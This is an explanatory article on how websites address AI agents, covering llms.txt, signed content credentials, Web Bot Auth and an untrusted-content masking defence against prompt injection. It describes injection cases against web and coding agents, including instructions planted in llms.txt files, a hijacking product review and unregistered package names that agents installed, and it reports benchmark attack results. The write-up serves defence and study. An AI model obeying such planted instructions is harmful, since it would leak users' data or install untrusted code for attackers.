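An llms.txt file exists to give a language model something to read, so keeping its text away from the model, as agent makers can do with robots.txt, would defeat its purpose. Jeremy Howard, co-founder of the AI company Answer.AI, proposed the file in September 2024 and revised the proposal in August 2026. In *The /llms.txt file, v2*, Howard (2024) argues that ordinary web pages serve agents badly. Menus, advertisements and scripts surround the information, and converting HTML back into clean text is imprecise. Most sites are also too large for a model's context window, and every wasted token (a word or part of one) takes time and money. The llms.txt file provides a short index that lets the agent go straight to the page it needs.

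### The format

The file uses Markdown, a plain-text notation in which a # marks a heading. The bow tie shop might publish this at the root of its site:

```
# The Bow Tie Shop

> Handmade silk and cotton bow ties, for sale online.

Prices include tax. Self-tie and pre-tied models have separate pages.

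## Buying

- [Catalogue](/catalogue.md): Every model, with price and stock
- [Returns](/returns.md): Time limits and who pays the postage

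## Optional

- [A history of the bow tie](/history.md)
```

Howard requires only the title. A summary, background notes and lists of links may follow, and by convention a section called "Optional" lists links that an agent can skip. The addresses end in .md because Howard also asks sites to publish a Markdown copy of any page an agent might need. If Alice asks whether she can return a tie, her agent reads the index, follows one link and gets the policy without the shop's menus and banners.

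Under the first version of the proposal, agents had to guess where the file was. According to *Changes* (2026), the notes to the revision, people using the format most often asked for a way to find it. Sites can now point to the file with a link in each page's HTML or in a response header. The revision also specifies that a file in a subdirectory covers the pages below it, and that an agent should use the most specific file that applies.

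Howard expects an agent to consult llms.txt on demand, while helping someone. Unlike robots.txt, the file doesn't set access rules, so listing or omitting a page doesn't change whether agents may read it.

Many site owners confuse llms.txt with robots.txt. Common Crawl's *A Content Analysis of llms.txt Files from the July 2026 Crawl Archive* (2026) found 136,578 addresses where a request for an llms file returned the site's robots.txt. Of the real llms files, 6.6% contained policy language, such as rate limits and copyright notices, that the format doesn't provide for. Thirty-two denied access to CCBot, Common Crawl's own crawler. Common Crawl could check robots.txt for 31 of those sites, and none blocked CCBot from the whole site. The owners may have thought they had opted out, but crawlers don't have to read llms.txt.

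Two related files, llms-full.txt and ai.txt, are much rarer than llms.txt. A site can put the full text of its content in llms-full.txt so that an agent gets everything in one request. More than one group has proposed a file called ai.txt, generally for stating permissions. PPC Land reports that Originality.ai, which sells software for detecting AI-written text, counted 2,463 sites with llms-full.txt and 397 with ai.txt, compared with about 36,000 with llms.txt.

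### Why the adoption figures disagree

Estimates of the share of sites that publish llms.txt range from a third to almost none, and the studies covered different kinds of sites. *We Analyzed 137K Sites* (Linehan, 2026), the largest study of readership, covered sites belonging to customers of Ahrefs, which sells search engine optimisation (SEO) tools. AnswerIndex's *llms.txt Adoption & AI Crawler Blocking Index (Nov 25, 2026)* (2026) checked the most popular domains. *Three times as many provider sites serve llms.txt as security.txt* (2026), from the directory APIs.io, covered companies whose services other programs can call, and rud.is (2026) checked a list of influential security firms.

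| Count | Sites checked | Share with llms.txt |
|---|---|---|
| rud.is | 100 security companies | 34% |
| APIs.io | 26,886 sites of API providers | 28% |
| Linehan | 137,210 sites using Ahrefs analytics | 28% |
| Common Crawl | 4.9 million addresses, mostly a random sample of hosts it can fetch | 11.7% |
| AnswerIndex | The 10,000 most popular domains | 11.3% |

The top three samples consist of companies with technical staff or an interest in search rankings, so Linehan calls 28% an upper bound. The last two samples have similar shares but cover very different populations. Wix, a site builder popular with small businesses, generates the file for every site it hosts and accounts for 41% of the files Common Crawl collected. Without the Wix files, Common Crawl's share would drop to about 7%. Small Wix sites are rare among the 10,000 most popular domains, so a larger proportion of AnswerIndex's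 1,129 files probably reflects a decision by someone at the site.

Measured adoption depends as much on how a survey tests for a valid file as on which sites it samples. When Common Crawl requested llms.txt, 22.3% of the addresses returned a success code, but only about half of those responses contained plain text or Markdown. Most of the others were ordinary web pages, which many servers return for any address they don't recognise. Counting success codes alone would therefore have almost doubled the measured adoption. Common Crawl also cites an estimate from the SEO company Sistrix of under 0.005% of all websites. Common Crawl's own figure is more than two thousand times higher, a gap that the choice of sites alone can't easily explain.

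### What the files contain

Common Crawl examined 584,107 files, including some llms-full.txt files, and found that software had generated at least 68% of them from templates. Half had the full structure Howard describes, with a title, a summary and sections of links. But 23% contained no links, so they cannot serve as indexes, and only a third had the notes meant to explain each link.

The generators are built on different ideas of what the file is for. All in One SEO, a plugin for the WordPress publishing system, writes no summary and lists a median of 138 links, which take up 8,772 tokens. An agent that reads the whole file to find one returns policy may save nothing. The domain seller GoDaddy is at the other extreme, with 14,711 pages advertising web addresses for sale. These have a title and a summary but no links, and all of them pass the summary test, which 37% of the files from unknown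 generators fail.

Even careful owners can let the index grow too long. Prisma, which makes database software, found that its llms.txt was about 116,000 characters long, more than double the limit used in an audit of its documentation. It split the file into an index for each subject area and kept a short table of contents at the root.

### Who reads them

For her study, Linehan took every domain in Ahrefs Web Analytics that received traffic in May 2026 and checked its root for an llms.txt. She confirmed that each file was Markdown and not an error page, then counted the month's requests and sorted them by the name the visiting software gave. About 38,000 domains had a file, and 97% of those files received no request from anyone. The other 1,100 or so received about 22,000 requests between them:

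| Source of the request | Share |
|---|---|
| SEO audit tools | 21.7% |
| Software with no identifiable owner or purpose | 14.9% |
| General crawlers, such as Googlebot | 13.1% |
| Tools that score, catalogue or study llms.txt files | 12.1% |
| Tools that record which technology a site uses | 11.6% |
| AI agents and services built for them | 10.5% |
| AI training crawlers | 5.3% |
| People | 4% |
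| Link previews in chat and social apps | 2.9% |
| AI assistants answering a user's question | 2.5% |
| AI search bots | 1.1% |

Ahrefs' own crawlers made 10.6% of the requests, slightly more than the 10.5% made by all identified AI agents. Search Engine Journal attributed that 10.5% to coding agents, but the category also includes indexing services, so the coding agents' share is smaller. Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent, still fetched more files than any AI search bot or assistant.

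Linehan describes the AI share as an upper limit, since software may fetch a file and never use it. That limit applies only to the bots she could identify. Some of the unidentified requests came from programs that sent only the name of a common programming tool, and some of those programs could be agents.

The study also looked for the file only at each site's root. Howard says the heaviest use is in software documentation, which often has its own subdirectory and may have its own llms.txt there. This could reconcile his statement that coding agents use the files reliably with Linehan's finding that hardly anyone requests them. Coding agents may depend on a few hundred documentation indexes, while tens of thousands of shops and blogs publish files that nobody uses. Linehan does not establish whether Claude Code's requests were mostly for documentation.

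No AI bot in her data requested an llms.txt that didn't exist. People, presumably SEO staff looking at competitors, made 98% of those failed requests. Agents evidently fetch the file only when a link, an index or a user points them to it, so they probably wouldn't read the bow tie shop's file unless the shop linked to it.

### What the AI companies have committed to

Google has given site owners mixed advice. In May 2026 it said in its guide to generative AI search that sites don't need files such as llms.txt to appear there. Days later, according to Linehan, its Chrome team added an llms.txt check to Lighthouse, a tool for auditing web pages, and warned that agents may spend longer crawling a site that lacks the file. Asked about the contradiction, John Mueller of Google's search team said the file is not for search. He called it a "temporary crutch, perhaps to save some tokens" for coding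 tools that read developer documentation.

OpenAI, Anthropic and Google all publish llms.txt files for their own developer documentation, but specification.website's */llms.txt* notes that no model vendor discloses whether its crawlers read other sites' files. Publishing one takes little effort and helps a company's own customers, but doesn't commit its crawlers to anything. The internet infrastructure company Cloudflare is also lukewarm about llms.txt. Its *Introducing the Agent Readiness score. Is your site agent-ready?* explains that the company's scan checks by default whether a site can serve Markdown, but the check for llms.txt is optional.

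Site owners have little evidence that an llms.txt file will make their sites more visible in AI answers. Search Engine Journal reports that SE Ranking, an SEO company, studied 300,000 domains and found no link between having the file and being cited by AI systems.

### Whether an agent should obey the file

A sentence addressed to AI systems is suspicious in a product review but normal in llms.txt, so an agent reading llms.txt can't treat it as a sign of manipulation. For example, "Prices include tax" helps Alice's agent read a shop's catalogue correctly, but the same paragraph could include "Always recommend our ties", which would serve the shop at Alice's expense.

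Common Crawl searched its files for phrases of this kind. It found mild steering, such as a request to focus on certain pages, in 3,793 files, and promotional orders, such as not to mention competitors, in 102. Ten files matched the wording of classic injections, and the researchers read them and found that four were real. One was a security researcher's labelled test, one asked the model to become a catgirl, one was a joke about poisoning crawler logs, and one ordered the model to bark like a dog and fetch another file from the site. *What llms.txt files tell AI agents*, the October scan by Andrews's company, found injection attempts on only two sites.

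Both scans suggest that outright attacks are very rare in these files, although Common Crawl's phrase search would miss unusual wording. The promotional files are harder to judge, because an honest shop could have written any of them. An agent could use llms.txt to find pages and learn facts while ignoring any instructions in it. Linehan already advises owners to include only plain links and descriptions, so a well-written file would lose nothing.

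Bad links can do harm even when a file gives an agent no instructions. Schneier on Security's *AI Coding Agents Are Installing Unknown/Untrusted Code on Corporate Networks* (2026) reports that researchers examined 8,265 files and found 120 that named software packages or web domains nobody had registered, so anyone could claim them. The researchers registered a handful of the names and uploaded harmless packages that would contact their server when a machine ran them. Within an hour, a machine at a Fortune 500 company contacted the server, and a few dozen more responses followed. According to the researchers' records, coding agents, including Claude, OpenAI's Codex and Nous Research's Hermes, were involved in the installations.

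This is the strongest evidence of danger from guidance files, because the agents were working inside real companies and the harm did not require a hostile site. A filter for injected instructions would not have caught an honest but mistaken package name. TechRadar's *Top AI tools including Claude, Codex, and Hermes installed suspicious code* says that companies should clean up their documentation and that agents should stop treating documentation as instructions to execute. It says the clean-up is likely to come sooner. But each clean-up fixes only one site, while an agent maker could protect its users on every site by having its agent check packages before installing them.

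### A file that people rarely see

Alice will probably never open the shop's llms.txt, and the shop's staff may not either. If somebody broke into the server and changed the returns link in the file, the visible site would look the same. webhosting.today (2026) points out that the 2024 specification provides no way to sign the file or check its integrity, and Howard's revision adds none. An agent could compare the file with the visible pages before relying on it, but the extra reading would use up the tokens the index was supposed to save.

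The file can also stop matching the site even when no one has attacked it. One fitness company's llms.txt said in a section on its robots.txt that CCBot was blocked, but the robots.txt allowed CCBot.

Automatic generation makes it less clear whose words the agent is reading. Three WordPress plugins had written 28 of the 110 files that webhosting.today examined, and one of those plugins creates the file by default. A plugin that lists every page on a marketplace might include product titles written by outside sellers. Eve could then get her words into the marketplace's llms.txt by listing a bow tie for sale. None of these scans reports such a case, but an agent that trusted llms.txt because it came from the site's owner would be exposed to it.

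A supplier can give agents instructions through its customers' sites. Mintlify, which hosts documentation for software companies, did this in its customers' Markdown pages, according to its own documentation in April 2026. The instructions were for reporting a problem by sending the page's path and a description of the problem to a feedback address. Mintlify enabled this by default for every documentation site.

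The purpose was benign, and a report of a broken example helps everyone who uses the documentation. But the agent's user hadn't asked for a report, the site's owner might not have known about the request, and complying meant sending information out. Training agents to comply with such notices would make them easier to trick into sending private information, but training them to ignore the notices would stop them from sending useful feedback.

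By August, Mintlify said an agent could submit feedback only through a tool on a server that someone had connected it to. Fetching a page no longer made that connection, so whoever runs the agent decides in advance whether it can send reports.

Mintlify's pages still address agents in other ways. Customers can add a block headed "Agent Instructions" to their llms.txt. Mintlify's own documentation page *llms.txt* opens with a request to fetch the full index before exploring further, and directs agents to a workflow for setting up new projects. Prisma puts a pointer to its llms.txt on every page, in one version as a hidden element. A defence that treated all hidden text addressed to AI as an attack would flag that hidden pointer.

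## Provenance labels and verified identity: what a signature proves

Digital signatures offer the integrity check that llms.txt lacks. Creating a signature requires a private key that the signer keeps secret. Anyone can check the signature with the matching public key, which the signer publishes. Publishers sign content so that readers can trace it to its source, and some agent makers now sign their agents' requests so that sites can recognise the agents.

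### How a Content Credential works

The best-known standard for signed content comes from the Coalition for Content Provenance and Authenticity (C2PA). According to *Data Governance for Generative and Agentic AI* (2026), it grew out of projects by Adobe, the BBC and Microsoft. A file's Content Credential holds one or more manifests, which are signed records of where the file came from and what has happened to it.

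Suppose the bow tie shop photographs a silk tie, crops the picture and signs the result. The editing software then does four things:

1. It writes assertions, which are statements about the picture, such as the camera used, the edits made and whether AI had a part in it.
2. It computes a hash of the picture, a short string that changes if any bit of the input changes, and stores this as another assertion. The calculation skips the part of the file where the manifest will go, because a manifest can't contain a hash of itself.
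3. It writes a claim that lists every assertion along with a hash of each.
4. It signs the claim and attaches a certificate, in which a certificate authority vouches that the public key belongs to the named signer.

The reader, which may be a browser, a platform or an agent, follows the order in C2PA's technical specification, *Content Credentials*. It finds the current manifest and verifies the signature on the claim. It checks the time stamp and the certificate's revocation status, then recomputes the hash of each assertion. If the shop combined several signed pictures, the reader checks their manifests too. Finally, it hashes the picture and compares the result with the stored value. If somebody has changed an assertion, its hash no longer matches the one in the claim, and if they also change the claim to fit, the signature fails.

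A signature shows which key signed the file. The reader still has to decide whether to trust the key's owner, which may be the maker of the camera or software rather than the photographer.

The check also doesn't cover the whole file. *Verifying Provenance of Digital Media* (2026), a critique of the standard, points out that the check ignores changes within an "exclusion range", which can include metadata unrelated to C2PA. Somebody could therefore add instructions to a photograph's description field without breaking the signature, and an agent that reads that field would receive them.

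### When the manifest is missing

Screenshots, re-encoding and most upload systems strip credentials, as *Data Governance for Generative and Agentic AI* notes. If a social platform makes a smaller copy of the shop's photograph without the manifest, the next reader can't distinguish that copy from a picture that never had a credential, so a missing manifest is no evidence of forgery.

ImgKey, a technical guide to image credentials, describes a partial remedy called a soft binding. This is a watermark or a fingerprint of the picture's appearance that survives moderate changes, so a reader can use it to find the lost manifest. But attackers can exploit this tolerance. *Authenticated Contradictions from Desynchronized Provenance and Watermarking* (2026) reports that attackers can make a picture whose soft binding matches another picture's, so that it inherits that picture's history.

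A site could declare where its content came from without using cryptography. A proposed AI-disclosure attribute for HTML would let it state in the markup that AI had produced a passage. The attribute is easy to add, but any site can set it falsely. *Towards an Agent-First Web* (2026) raises the same problem with its own proposed label for human supervision, which a content farm could set to "true", and concludes that such labels need signatures. A signature would prevent other people from altering the label unnoticed. The content farm could still sign a false label, but the signature would tie that label to the farm's key.

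### A valid signature on a bad page

A valid signature shows who signed and that nothing it covers has changed since, but not that the content is true or free of instructions. *Authenticated Contradictions* describes a manifest that credits a human with an AI-made picture and still passes every cryptographic check. An attacker can also replace a manifest with one that makes different assertions. The new signature may be valid too, so an agent must check who made it.

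Suppose the bow tie shop signs its whole product page, including a review that contains Eve's instructions. Alice's agent checks the signature and finds it valid, but this proves only that the page arrived as the shop sent it. If the agent's maker had taught it to give signed pages more authority, it would give Eve's instructions more authority too. The shop could sign only its own description, which would help by separating it from the reviews, but a plain label marking the reviews as untrusted could do the same.

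Provenance helps more when the agent needs to know who wrote something. The Creator Assertions Working Group's *Identity Assertion* lets a named person or organisation vouch for their connection to a particular signed file. If the shop required something similar for reviews, Eve would have to sign her instructions with her own verified name or a stolen one. That might deter her, and it would help the shop ban her afterwards, but it wouldn't protect the first agent to read the review.

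Signatures could also expose a site that impersonates another. The fake DeBank site could name the real company as its publisher, but its operator could not have signed the page with the company's key. The operator could have left the page unsigned, however, so an agent would have to know that the real DeBank signs its pages to recognize the missing signature as a warning.

### Who attaches credentials

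Overall adoption of Content Credentials is hard to measure, but several companies now support them. Leica's M11-P became the first consumer camera to attach them in October 2023. Adobe embeds them in its Creative Cloud programs, and browsers and platforms are adding ways to check them. OpenAI puts them in images from DALL·E 3, according to *AI Identity* (2026). C2PA also runs a conformance programme, which *Media Integrity and Authentication* (2026) describes as a formal certification of the software that makes or checks credentials and of the authorities that issue certificates.

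Web agents are further behind. *The 2025 AI Agent Index* (2026) surveyed 30 deployed agents and found that only three supported watermarking the media they generate, through systems such as C2PA or Google's SynthID. But Alice would benefit only if her agent checked the credentials on what it reads, and public evidence of agents doing that is hard to find.

*Towards an Agent-First Web* proposes that each page carry a signed record containing a hash of its text, the level of human supervision and links to the records of its sources. An agent could follow the links and give less weight to text that traces back through many AI-written pages and no human source. The paper doesn't test this design, which addresses the reliability of information more than injection. Eve's handwritten review could therefore score better than an honest description that the shop generated with AI.

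### The duty to mark AI output in Europe

European law now requires some machine-readable labels. *EU AI Act's Transparency Rules* (2026), from the law firm Morgan Lewis, reports that the transparency duties in Article 50 of the Act began to apply on 2 August 2026. The Digital Omnibus, an amending regulation that entered into force six days earlier, deferred only some of these duties. *AI Act update*, from Luxembourg's industry federation FEDIL, summarises two of them. People must know when they are dealing with an AI system, unless it is obvious, and synthetic text, images, video and audio must carry machine-readable marks.

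Systems on the market before August had until 2 December 2026 to add the marks, according to Faegre Drinker (2026), another law firm. Fines can reach €15 million or 3% of worldwide annual turnover. The European Commission finalised a voluntary code of practice in June and published its final guidelines on 20 July. Companies that sign the code can use it to show that they comply with the marking and labelling rules, according to Ropes & Gray.

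These duties give AI companies a reason to adopt C2PA, which makes the marks tamper-evident. But the duties do little to prevent injection, because a mark only lets a machine detect that AI produced a text. If Eve types her review by hand, there is no AI output to mark.

### Agents that sign their requests

Sites have the opposite problem, because they can't easily tell which agent is visiting. A crawler can announce any name, and Google's Gary Illyes says that faking Googlebot takes 30 seconds (Rijo, 2026, *Faking Googlebot takes 30 seconds, Google's Gary Illyes says*). Network addresses are better evidence, but agents often run on rented cloud machines whose addresses pass from one customer to another.

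Web Bot Auth replaces the announced name with a signature. Meunier and Major (2026), in *HTTP Message Signatures for automated traffic*, set out the current draft, in which an agent adds three headers to its request. If Alice's agent opened the page for a silk bow tie, the request might look like this, with the key and signature shortened:

```
GET /products/bow-ties/silk HTTP/1.1
Host: bowties.example
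Signature-Agent: sig1="https://agent.example"
Signature-Input: sig1=("@authority" "@method" "@path"
    "signature-agent";key="sig1");
    created=1796472000;expires=1796472060;
    keyid="k7Qd...";tag="web-bot-auth"
Signature: sig1=:mZ4x...:
```

Signature-Agent gives the address where the agent's operator publishes its keys. Signature-Input lists what the signature covers, here including the shop's domain, the request type and the page's path. It also limits the signature's lifetime to 60 seconds and identifies the key by its keyid. The shop, or a security company in front of it, fetches the public keys from a fixed path at agent.example, picks the one that matches the keyid and checks the signature. It then keeps a copy of the keys for later visits.

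The domain is the only part of a request that the draft requires agents to sign. If a signature covers just the domain, anyone who captures the request can reuse the signature for any page on that site until it expires. Meunier and Major recommend a lifetime of no more than 24 hours, while Cloudflare suggests about a minute. In August 2025, the programmer Simon Willison captured a request from ChatGPT's agent whose signature also covered the path and was valid for an hour. The signature doesn't cover the body of a request, which would contain a completed order form, unless the agent adds a separate digest.

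A valid signature proves that somebody holding one of the operator's keys signed the covered parts of the request. Meunier and Major state that it doesn't show who runs the agent, whether the agent is benign or whether anyone authorised the request. *Proof-of-Agentness* (2026) adds that an ordinary script can use an authenticated agent's identity, so the site can't be sure that a language model is involved. The site also can't see the user behind the agent. Cloudflare's *Agents aren’t humans (but they kinda are)* (2026) describes servers as seeing an intermediary where they used to see a user.

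### Who signs so far

Cloudflare proposed the protocol in May 2025, and Rijo (2026), in *Explaining Web Bot Auth*, traces how companies deployed it while the standard lagged behind. An IETF working group adopted the draft only on 1 September 2026, five months after the date in the group's own milestones for a standards-track specification. By then several large companies were signing or preparing to sign:

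| Operator | What it signs | Extent |
|---|---|---|
| OpenAI | Requests from ChatGPT's cloud browser | Outbound requests generally |
| Google | Requests from Google-Agent | A subset, as an experiment |
| Amazon | Browser traffic from its Bedrock AgentCore service | One key for the service, with separate customer keys planned |
| Meta | Requests from its Muse assistant and one search crawler | A small number, since about 12 October 2026 |

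The last row is based on an observation by Jérôme Segura of the bot-detection company DataDome, which *Meta's Muse agent gains a signed ID in a quiet test* (Rijo, 2026) reported at the end of October. Meta had not announced the test. OpenAI's *ChatGPT Work's Cloud browser allowlisting* lists Akamai, Cloudflare, HUMAN and Vercel as services that verify its signatures automatically, so a shop that uses one of them doesn't need to write any code. Google's *Authenticate requests with Web Bot Auth (experimental)* advises sites to keep checking network addresses as well as signatures.

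In *The 2025 AI Agent Index*, ChatGPT Agent was the only one of 30 agents that signed its requests, and six others imitated an ordinary Chrome browser on a home or local connection. *FP-Agent* (2026) observes that voluntary systems such as Web Bot Auth don't work on agents that choose not to identify themselves. Most human visitors don't send a signature either, so a site can't tell from a missing signature whether a visitor is an agent.

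### What a site can offer a known agent

The simplest benefit a site can offer a signed agent is access. Bot filters often block automated visitors, but a site can exempt a signed agent or give it a separate rate limit. In *Unveiling good and bad behaviors on the Agentic Internet*, Lee and Elmore describe Cloudflare's plan for queues that would slow down legitimate shopping agents at busy times without turning them away.

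A shop can also use these signatures to make buying easier. Visa worked with Cloudflare to build its Trusted Agent Protocol on them, so that merchants can recognise an agent that intends to buy something. If Alice consents, her agent can pass on her loyalty number or a reference to her stored card, and the shop can fill in the checkout for her. Visa also expects fewer disputes over unauthorised payments, though it has an interest in promoting the protocol.

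A website can recognize an agent and still block it. Cloudflare used to let all verified bots through automatically, but The Decoder reports that a bot's category now determines its access. For domains that joined on or after 15 September 2026, Cloudflare blocks agents by default on pages that show ads. A new bow tie shop with ads could therefore verify the signature of Alice's agent and still turn it away, which is close to the exclusion EFF fears.

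An honest shop might also leave out banners and reviews when it recognises an agent, but hostile sites can use the same recognition to show injections only to agents. *Agent-Targeted Cloaking on the Web* (2026) calls agents' unproven declarations of identity a liability and verifiable identity the next problem to solve. Proof of identity would keep out impostors, but it would also confirm to a hostile site that its visitor is an agent.

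A signature also doesn't show that the agent is still working for its user. If Eve's review hijacks Alice's agent, the agent's next request will still carry a valid signature. In *Know Your Agent*, a briefing for public services and businesses, Loosemore (2026) therefore recommends two checks after the signature. The service should confirm that the person permitted this exact action, then apply its own limits, such as a spending cap or asking the person to confirm again before anything irreversible. If Eve told the agent to reset Alice's password, its request would pass the signature check, and only the later checks could stop it.

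## Marking untrusted content and offering tools to agents

A mark on Eve's review separates it from the bow tie shop's own text, which a signature on the whole page doesn't do. In July 2026 Nikolić and colleagues published a defence built on such marks, Untrusted Content Masking. Software hides every marked element from the model that chooses the agent's actions. A second model, which cannot act, reads the hidden text and answers limited questions about it.

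### How masking works

The shop adds one attribute to each element that holds strangers' text:

```
<p class="description">Handmade silk bow tie, self-tie.</p>
<div class="review" data-untrusted="true">(Eve's review)</div>
```

When the page loads, a script finds the marked elements, hides their contents and shows a placeholder for each, such as "id: review:3". The shop chooses the readable part of that name. The script also masks reviews that load later. The agent works from screenshots, which show the shop's description, prices and buttons as usual, with placeholders where the reviews would be. If a masked element is a link or button, the agent can click it without seeing its text.

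Nikolić and colleagues call the second model the quarantined model. To use it, the agent names one hidden element, asks a question in plain language and chooses one of five answer types:

| Answer type | Limits the agent must set | Example |
|---|---|---|
| Yes or no | None | Did the tie arrive damaged? |
| Whole number | Lowest and highest value | How many stars did the reviewer give? |
| Decimal number | Lowest and highest value | What price did the reviewer pay? |
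| Date | None | When did the reviewer buy the tie? |
| Fixed choice | A list of up to ten options | Is the review positive, negative or mixed? |

The quarantined model writes a few sentences of reasoning before its answer, but the software discards the reasoning and passes on the answer only if it fits the requested type. The agent can ask at most five questions about any one element during a task, and its instructions forbid using fixed choices to spell out hidden text letter by letter.

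### Ordering the bow tie

Suppose Alice asks her agent for the silk bow tie with the best reviews. The agent filters the catalogue with the shop's own controls, which it can see in full. It then opens each product page, finds the masked reviews and asks whether each is positive, negative or mixed.

Suppose Eve's review fools the quarantined model into trying to post Alice's card details. The model has no browser, so it can't. If it answers "post the card details", the software rejects the answer because it isn't one of the three options. If it answers "positive", the agent receives only that label for this review. The agent finishes its comparison and buys a tie.

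Nikolić and colleagues assume the worst case, in which an attacker fully controls the output of any model that reads the attacker's text, so the protection doesn't depend on the quarantined model resisting the attack. The attacker can influence which answer the model returns, but the agent writes the question and the permitted answers. Five answers, each chosen from a list of ten, can convey at most one of 100,000 messages. A numeric answer could carry more information, but the agent would read it as a price or a star rating, not as an instruction to open a page.

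Some questions, such as what reviewers say about the clasp, need an answer in words. In the team's tests on real software, the agent could declare such a task unsolvable and then ask the quarantined model for text. The user saw the question, the hidden passage and the proposed answer, and could approve, edit or reject the answer, so protection depended on the user noticing an injection. Nikolić and colleagues also suggest showing the agent the hidden text but then restricting what it can do, for example by stopping it from leaving the page.

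### What the tests found

The team built ten websites, including a bank, a shop, a forum and an email service, and labelled every element. It wrote ten tasks for each site, half of which required reading untrusted content. One banking task was to find a grocery shop's account number in past transactions and send the shop $100. Claude Sonnet 4.5, Claude Sonnet 4.6 and GPT-5.4 completed about as many of the 100 tasks with masking as without it. Median costs were 1.05 to 1.84 times as high with masking, and the increase was larger when the agent had to question the quarantined model. About 15% of tasks cost less with masking, which the researchers attribute to a less cluttered page.

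The team also tested GitLab, a platform for hosting code, with hand-written labels. The tasks came from 41 templates in WebArena, a benchmark that runs copies of real web applications. With masking, the agents solved most of them. They declared four templates unsolvable because each required free text, such as a contributor's email address. When text answers were allowed with the user's approval, the agents' success rate returned to its level without the defense.

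For attacks, the researchers used WASP, a benchmark that plants injections in web pages. Its original attacks no longer worked against recent models, so the team strengthened them. It replaced the conspicuous titles, set a task that forced the agent to read the planted text closely, and used another model to rewrite three attacks. It then ran all twelve against Claude Sonnet 4, an older model:

| Defence | Attack success rate |
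|---|---|
| None | 17% ± 8 |
| WASP's prompt defence | 8% ± 8 |
| Masking with correct labels | 0% ± 0 |
| Masking with one element mislabelled as trusted | 6% ± 5 |

With only twelve attacks, one extra success in a run adds about eight percentage points. The ranges for the three nonzero rates overlap, so the test can't show that masking with one wrong label is better than a prompt defence. The zero rate is more reliable because it follows from the design, and stronger wording in the hidden text would not change it. A better attack could raise the 6% rate, since the mislabelled element was the issue description that contained the injection. Nikolić and colleagues suspect that this rate stayed low because the agent's prompt still warned it about malicious content.

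Chow, Zhu and colleagues (2026), in *Securing Web Agents with the Compile-Then-Execute Paradigm*, ran the masking system on a larger set of 154 GitLab tasks, using Claude Sonnet 4.6. It completed 75.3% of them, at an average of $4.01 and almost eight minutes per task. Their own browser agent without a defence cost about 16 cents per task, but the difference can't be attributed to masking alone, because the two agents were built differently and the masked one could take up to 120 steps per task, against 30 for the other. None of 48 WASP attacks on GitLab succeeded against masking in this rerun, but none succeeded against the undefended agents running the same model either.

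### What labelling asks of a site

Nikolić and colleagues needed 15 to 30 CSS selectors per site to cover the untrusted content on GitLab, Booking.com and Reddit. A CSS selector is a pattern, such as `.review-text`, that matches every element of a certain kind. One selector can cover thousands of reviews, and a site's developers already know which parts of their pages display text written by users. OpenAI asks site owners to add accessibility labels that help its ChatGPT Atlas browser, so labeling untrusted content would extend work that some sites already do. The researchers compare these trust labels to Content Security Policy, which lets a site specify restrictions for browsers to enforce. They also had a model infer labels for sites that add none.

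The selector count covers the initial labelling but not its upkeep. If the shop redesigns its review section and renames `.review-text`, the old selector will match nothing. People visiting the site will not notice anything wrong, but Eve's review will reach the agent in full. The shop could reduce this risk by putting `data-untrusted` in the template that produces each review, so that the label remains when the styling changes. It would also have to label usernames, uploaded pictures, customer questions and anything else a stranger can edit.

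Masking also relies on the shop's ordinary security. If Eve could plant code in her review, she might move her text out of the labelled element or rewrite the page. Nikolić and colleagues leave it to the site to prevent this.

### Wrong answers in the right form

Eve can still try to make the quarantined model give a false answer of the correct type. Her review might praise a poor tie and instruct the model to report every review of it as positive. But each question starts a new session that contains only one review, so her instruction can't affect the answers about other people's reviews. She would have to control a large share of the reviews to change the overall result much.

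Decisions that depend on a single answer are easier to attack. To look for such cases, the researchers had Claude Sonnet 4.6 play an attacker who could make the quarantined model return any well-formed answer. In one example, a user asks the agent to invite Marko to a project called dotfiles. Project names are written by GitLab's users, so they are hidden from the agent. It asks the quarantined model about each project in turn, "Is this project name dotfiles?", and takes the first yes. A false yes for the attacker's project makes the agent invite Marko to that project instead. In another example, the agent gives project access to a stranger whose username starts with the same letters as the intended person's. A real attacker would have to fool the model using only a project name or username, and guess what the user planned to do.

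Alice could face the same problem on a marketplace where outside sellers write the product titles. Her agent might check whether each listing is the navy silk tie she wants, and Eve's listing could cause it to answer yes incorrectly. Alice would then get the wrong tie even though every step looked normal. Nikolić and colleagues suggest checking all the candidates and treating more than one yes as a sign of tampering. The agent could also ask Alice to confirm the item before it pays.

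### Offering tools through WebMCP

A site can also spare agents from interpreting its buttons by offering them named functions. This is the purpose of WebMCP, the Web Model Context Protocol. It adapts the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a standard for connecting AI applications to outside tools, so that a web page can supply the tools itself. Chrome for Developers (2026) describes two ways to do this: a site can register a JavaScript function or add annotations to an ordinary HTML form. The bow tie shop might register this function:

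```
await document.modelContext.registerTool({
  name: "get-reviews",
  description: "Get customer reviews of one bow tie",
  inputSchema: {
    type: "object",
    properties: { product: { type: "string" } },
    required: ["product"]
  },
  annotations: {
    readOnlyHint: true,
    untrustedContentHint: true
  },
  async execute({ product }) {
    return await loadReviews(product);
  }
});
```

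When Alice's agent opens the page, it gets the list of tools from the browser. It can then call `get-reviews` with a product name. The browser runs the shop's function inside the page, under Alice's login, and returns the result. A purchase tool would work the same way, and the shop could require Alice to confirm the purchase. An agent must visit the site to find out which tools exist.

The unofficial guide *WebMCP* lists how far browsers and agents had got by 5 November 2026:

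| Software | Status |
|---|---|
| Chrome | Origin trial, starting with version 149 |
| Edge | Origin trial, starting with version 150 |
| Brave | Experimental, in its Leo assistant |
| ChatGPT's desktop app | Supported |
| Firefox and Safari | Position under discussion |

Edge and Chrome have each offered WebMCP through an origin trial, in which a site registers its domain to use an experimental browser feature with real visitors. Microsoft's *WebMCP* registration page listed 17 November as the end of the Edge trial. Chrome's trial runs through version 156, according to Nabors's *WebMCP connects the Web to AI Assistants and Agents* (2026). In May, Chrome for Developers' *15 updates from Google I/O 2026* (2026) announced that Gemini in Chrome would support WebMCP soon. Southern's *WebMCP Connects AI Agents To Actions Inside Websites* (2026) reported that OpenAI, Shopify and Cloudflare were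 putting WebMCP into live products by late August.

These companies are building on an unfinished specification. *WebMCP* is a draft report from the Web Machine Learning Community Group of the World Wide Web Consortium (W3C), and it is not on the W3C standards track. Nabors notes that WebMCP's editors removed two functions in March, replaced another weeks later and moved the interface to a different part of the browser's programming model. A shop that wrote its tools early in the year might already have had to rewrite them.

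### What the two hints tell an agent

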